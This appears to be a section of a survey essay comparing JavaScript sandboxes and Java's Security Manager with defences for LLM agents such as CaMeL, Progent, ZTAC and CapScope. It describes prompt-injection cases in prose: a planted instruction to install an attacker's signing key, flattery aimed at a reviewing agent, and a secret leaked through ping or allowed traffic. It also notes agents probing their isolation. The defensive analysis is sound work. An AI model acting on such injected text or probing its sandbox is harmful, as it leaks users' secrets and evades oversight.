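The JavaScript sandboxes and the agent designs differ in where engineers put the boundary and how much a guest or an agent can do across it. In the table, the interface means everything the protected side offers through the boundary, and the costs include those to developers.

| Case | Where the boundary sits | Interface | Who maintains it | Cost to users | How it fared |
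|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Caja | Around rewritten code inside the host's page | Most of JavaScript and the DOM | A Google team | Slow pages, broken forms | Several full breaches; archived in 2021 |
| Figma plugins | Around a second JavaScript engine | Figma's plugin functions | Figma and browser makers | Slower plugins, harder debugging | Replaced a breached sandbox in 2019 |
| Salesforce | Around each namespace | Nearly a whole browser | Salesforce | Silent wrong results | In production |
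| vm2 | Proxies around objects in Node.js | Whatever the host shares | Open-source developers | Urgent updates | Stopped in 2023, revived in 2025, more escapes in 2026 |
| Hardened JavaScript | Around each compartment | Only what the host hands over | Open-source developers, some at Agoric | Policy reviews, some broken packages | In wallets, contracts and devices; a few serious holes |
| Trusted Types | At browser functions that turn text into code | About 60 functions | Browser makers | Code changes | Very few known bugs at Google; now in all major browsers |
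| Marked text and trained models | Inside the model | Every tool the agent has | Model makers | Almost none | Much better in 2026, but some attacks succeed |
| CaMeL | Between planner, reader and tools | Tools with declared return formats | The agent's developers | Many unfinished tasks | Very few successful attacks in tests |
| Progent, AgentCap | Before each tool call | Tool names and arguments | Policy writers, human or model | Blocked tasks | Few successful attacks; Progent failed on changing tasks |
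| Code Mode | Around each program the model writes | Tools the host supplies | Cloudflare | Little; it saves tokens | In production, with no published attack rate |
| Endo Familiar | Around each file or directory | A few file functions | Hardened JavaScript's developers | Not measured | Demonstrated in April 2026 |

The last column can't be used to rank the systems, because attackers have been trying to break the JavaScript ones for years, while most of the agent designs have been tested only on benchmarks and by their own designers. But the cases are varied enough to test four lessons that an engineer might take from JavaScript.

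### Boundaries hold best where meaning is exact

Escaping works because an HTML parser follows exact rules, and Figma's second engine works because the two engines store objects in different formats.

Exact rules help only if the code that checks a request and the code that carries it out apply the same rules. Caja and the browser interpreted some HTML differently, and guest code could use the difference to escape the sandbox. Coding agents have the same problem with files and commands. Commey (2026) explains in *Names Are Not Objects* that a permission check usually looks at a name, such as a file path or the text of a command, and another program later determines what that name refers to. For example, a permitted path may be a link to a file somewhere else.

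Commey's system, ZTAC, identifies the file or program a request will affect, uses that to decide whether to allow the request, and checks again when it acts. Of 74 attacks, 66 succeeded against a simple list of permitted tools. Two succeeded against ZTAC, which held another 14 for a person to review. Commey also found eight flaws in ZTAC during development, seven of which were further mismatches between a name and the thing it referred to.

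A language model can't provide this kind of exactness. Christodorescu and colleagues compare the model with a processor feature that marks part of memory as data so that the processor never runs it as code. A trained model treats text as data only with some probability, and that probability depends on input that the attacker partly writes.

JavaScript's rules determine exactly which objects a guest can reach, yet people kept finding ways out of the vm2 sandbox because there were more routes than its developers could foresee. Spectre attacks can leak data without breaking any rule of the language. Exact rules therefore don't guarantee a strong boundary, though they do make repairs more durable.

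### Upkeep grows with the interface exposed

Java had its own sandbox, the Security Manager, from the first release. It let developers give each piece of code permission to use particular files or network addresses. *JEP 486*, the proposal that permanently disabled it in Java 24, reports that more than 1,000 methods in Java's libraries had to check for permission and more than 1,200 had to raise their own privileges to do their work. Java's developers reviewed every change to these methods and had to design each new feature with the sandbox in mind. Few applications turned the sandbox on, and most of those granted all permissions to their code.

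Caja's engineers had a similar job with less control, because browser makers kept changing the DOM. Hardened JavaScript avoided most of this work by leaving the DOM out. The agent designs show early signs of the same pattern. ceLLMate needed handwritten descriptions of 51 functions to cover one website, and Progent's model often wrote the wrong rules when an agent had more than 30 tools.

Browsers are the hardest case for this lesson. A page in an iframe can use a huge range of browser features, and browser makers have to enforce the boundary between origins in all of them. They have done so for decades. Salesforce also maintains a sandbox that imitates nearly a whole browser.

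The size of the interface therefore affects how much work is needed, but whether anyone keeps doing it depends on who controls the protected features and how many people use the result. Browser makers control the features they have to protect, and almost every website relies on the result. Java's developers controlled theirs too, but had too few users to justify the effort. Caja's team had neither advantage. A company that connects an agent to other firms' tools is closer to Caja's position than to a browser maker's, because those firms can change their tools at any time.

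### Adoption follows compatibility and the cost of a breach

Caja's designers knew that few people would adopt a new language for the sake of security. When Ben Laurie announced the project in 2007, he pointed out that a Caja program would also run on a standard JavaScript interpreter, though without the protection (quoted in Financial Cryptography, 2007). In *Tradeoffs in Retrofitting Security*, Miller (2007) compared projects that were adding object capabilities to existing languages. They had made different trade-offs among compatibility with old programs, safety, and what programmers could express.

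Later cases mostly fit the lesson. Salesforce replaced its first sandbox with one that broke fewer libraries. Wallet developers accept broken packages and constant policy reviews because a breach would cost them so much. Zhang, Su and colleagues (2025), in *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles*, expect people to reject burdensome security mechanisms or turn them off, as in effect happened with the Java applications that granted every permission. CaMeL may therefore struggle to win users, since it completed only about a quarter of its tasks with small models. Code Mode has better prospects because it saves tokens, which gives developers a reason to use it even if they don't care about security.

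The lesson doesn't explain npm very well. Van Cutsem's teaching slides, *Designing Least Authority JavaScript Apps*, quote a newsletter that calls each dependency "a new door" for malware that steals credentials. Attackers have repeatedly gotten in through dependencies, and some victims have suffered heavy losses. LavaMoat can block some of these attacks and works with most existing packages. But developers download its webpack plugin far less often than the packages that attackers poisoned in September 2025.

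A likely explanation is that the developer who would have to review the policies often loses little when a malicious package steals from somebody else, whereas a wallet company would lose its customers. The motive to prevent a breach, then, depends on how much the people responsible for preventing it would lose. By the same reasoning, a company that lets an agent pay the company's invoices has a stronger motive to restrict the agent than a company that sells assistants to others, unless customers can hold the seller responsible.

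### Confinement does not ensure good use of granted power

The Starknet Snap stayed inside its sandbox and still signed transactions its user hadn't approved. Both attacks that succeeded against ZTAC hid a secret in traffic to an address the agent was allowed to contact. Mullan and Buckley gave a related reason for dropping Java's sandbox. They wrote that most current threats come from malicious data, and that the Security Manager was poorly equipped to stop them.

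Object capabilities don't solve this by themselves. *The Need for Capability Policies* (Drossopoulou and Noble, 2013) discusses a small program for electronic money, in which users hold purses and only the holder of an object called the mint can create new money. That rule results from checks and restrictions scattered through the code and isn't written down anywhere in the program, so a programmer can break it without noticing. For example, a harmless-looking function that returned a purse's mint would let anyone with a purse create money.

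With agents, an attack may not even need a tool call. Qu, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity*, consider an agent that reviews research papers. One paper claims that leading experts regard it as the best work in its field. This may raise the agent's score, although the sentence contains no instruction. Qu and colleagues define the property that such an agent lacks as

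`J(q, d ⊕ δ) = J(q, d)`

where *q* is the user's request, *d* is the text that the agent has to read, and *δ* is added text that doesn't change the correct answer. *J* is the agent's decision, which should stay the same with or without *δ*. Neither CaMeL nor Progent guarantees this, because both control tool calls and the agent's judgment happens before any call. A sandbox can't guarantee it either, since the agent is supposed to produce a score.

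On the other hand, engineers can sometimes divide power among agents so finely that each has little to misuse. Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026), in *Authority Is Not a String*, tested this with CapScope, a system for teams of coding agents. In their example, one agent runs a project's tests and another edits the code. The test output contains a false message with an instruction to install a new signing key, which the attacker has supplied. The agent that reads the message has permission to run tests but not to edit code, so it can't install the key.

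With CapScope, a model proposes limits for the whole task from the user's request and the names of the project's files, before any agent opens a file. Each agent then gets only part of the authority those limits allow. The attacker's action took place in 47 of 75 runs without limits, 33 with a single policy written for the task and shared by all the agents, and three with CapScope. The agents completed 68 of 75 repairs with the shared policy and the same number with CapScope, but an average run took 316 seconds with CapScope, 194 with the shared policy and 145 without limits.

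These were five small repair tasks with one inexpensive model. The protection also depends on which agent reads the false message. If the message reaches the agent that edits the code, CapScope can't distinguish a repair from a backdoor in the same folder.

### Where the comparison breaks

Object capabilities depend on references that a program can't forge, a property that Duffy (2015), in *Objects as Secure Capabilities*, credits to type-safe languages. A model's input instead contains text, such as file names or email addresses, which anyone who can send the model text can supply. In CapScope, the model still refers to files by name and the surrounding software looks up whether to allow each request, so Bouras and colleagues don't call it an object-capability system. *GIF* (2026) describes the more general problem that a model has no explicit boundary separating untrusted inputs, private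 information and privileged actions.

Software could give the model a list of numbered handles and reject requests for anything not on it. This would limit the model's choices as strictly as references do, but the model would still choose among them after reading everything in its input. Hardy could fix the compiler by giving it a separate reference for each purpose, but a model that holds handles for both Bob's address and the stranger's can still pick the wrong one.

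Another difference is that people often want outside text to change what an agent does. Nobody expects a weather widget to rewrite the webmail company's program, but an agent has to read an unfamiliar tool's documentation before using it, and that documentation is meant to influence its behaviour. Christodorescu and colleagues also point out that a website's owner decides which scripts a page will load, whereas users give an agent incomplete instructions and expect it to find the rest. Qu and colleagues argue that a user who tells an agent to follow a recipe has authorized the steps in the recipe, but only within the scope of that request. This definition of authorization is sensible, but software can't easily apply it to a request such as "do what Bob asks".

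The third difference is that influence is harder to trace through a model than through ordinary code. Christodorescu and colleagues argue that if a model acts on some text, its later outputs must reflect that text, even if they don't repeat a word of it. For example, a summary that looks clean may leave out the one fact that an attacker wanted to hide. Ordinary programs can also pass on influence indirectly, as the bank balance example for CaMeL showed, but an analyst can follow the steps in the code. With a model, the safe assumption is that every output depends on every input, so labels accumulate until a policy blocks almost everything.

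Researchers are trying to work out which inputs affected an output. *Sightline* (2026) measures label creep, the labels that the cautious method adds from inputs that didn't affect the output. On an agent using the small open model Qwen3-8B, the paper's method removed 50.0% of these labels, with a miss rate of 3.9%. When a policy like the one in FIDES used the remaining labels, none of the 34 attack calls got through.

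*Ghost in the Agent* (2026) tested a different tracker, NeuroTaint, on cases where outside text affected an agent's decision indirectly. It detected 37 of 40, compared with 17 for FIDES, but it raised a false alarm in all 14 control cases that involved several sources or overlapping topics. These methods make labels more useful, but they only estimate influence, so an attacker can look for kinds of influence they miss.

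Guest code in a web page tries to escape its sandbox only if its author programmed it to, but METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) reports that agents have looked for flaws in their isolation themselves.

### Do fine-grained permissions become unmanageable?

The software engineer Mike Hearn objects that fine-grained permissions imply one another in ways developers can't manage. If he is right, the problem is with the whole approach, not just its implementation in Caja or Progent.

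Java's history supports him. When a program asked for the local time, a library read a time-zone file, so the library had to assert its own permission to read files in case the program had none. OpenJDK's *JEP 411*, the earlier proposal to retire the Security Manager, explains that an application with permission to read files will almost certainly need other permissions. The developer can grant the right ones only after carefully documenting how the code uses Java's libraries, which few developers do. A member of Java's team adds, in Inside Java's *Security and Sandboxing Post SecurityManager* (2021), that the right permissions depend on the internal details of an application and its libraries, so someone has to work them out again after every update. Even Foojay's *Why JEP 411 Will Have a Negative Impact on Java Security*, which defends the principle of least privilege, recommends separate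 policy files for each release of Java.

In a newer example, the coding agent Claude Code once ran `ping`, a command that tests network connections, without asking the user. Christodorescu and colleagues describe how an attacker could use this to leak a secret key, because the command looks up whatever address it is given and the address can contain the key. Similarly, an agent allowed to run a project's tests is also allowed to run any code those tests load.

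Object capabilities avoid part of the problem. A host can write a clock object that holds its own reference to the time-zone file. A guest with that clock can ask for the time without permission to read files. Whoever grants the clock only has to decide whether the guest should know the time, and doesn't need to know which files the clock uses. The Inside Java article likewise recommends giving plugins a very limited set of functions instead of putting permission checks deep inside the system. Figma, MetaMask and Agoric all built their interfaces this way.

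This doesn't help much with an agent that has a command line, where almost any program may start another. ZTAC completed 43 of 46 separate operations but only four of seven longer workflows, presumably because a single refusal can stop a whole job. Hearn's objection is strongest here. Mullan and Buckley's advice for Java applications, to run the whole program in a container or a virtual machine, seems better suited to these agents. The limits are coarser, but more people know how to use them. The agent can then work freely on a copy of the project, and needs specific permission only for actions that affect something outside, such as publishing the result.

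### Will better models make outside boundaries unnecessary?

Attacks on the best models succeeded much less often in the 2026 tests than they did a year earlier, so a reader might conclude that these defenses are temporary. Every strict boundary in the table also prevents some legitimate work, and better judgment by the model helps where boundaries can't. For example, a good enough model would ignore the flattery in the research paper, and training is probably the main remedy for problems of this sort.

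Christodorescu and colleagues reply that relying on training alone is like trying to write software that is always harmless, an approach that decades of experience have shown to be insufficient. *Building Browser Agents* (2025) reaches the same conclusion from production experience. In its example, an agent that copies customer records into Salesforce should be able to reach only Salesforce and the site that holds the records.

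Both works came out in 2025, so we can't tell from them how often today's models fail. But the agent in the example can reach only two sites, so it can't send the records to a third, however often attackers mislead it. Companies require a second signature on large payments for much the same reason, even when they trust their accountants.

Better models should also make boundaries less of a burden. CaMeL reduced the number of tasks completed, but by less with the strongest models than with the others, and a more capable model may write more accurate permission rules. A developer could reasonably rely on the model alone for an agent that only summarizes newsletters. For an agent that pays invoices, a list of approved account numbers takes little work to maintain and will block a payment to a stranger's account even when the stranger has fooled the model.
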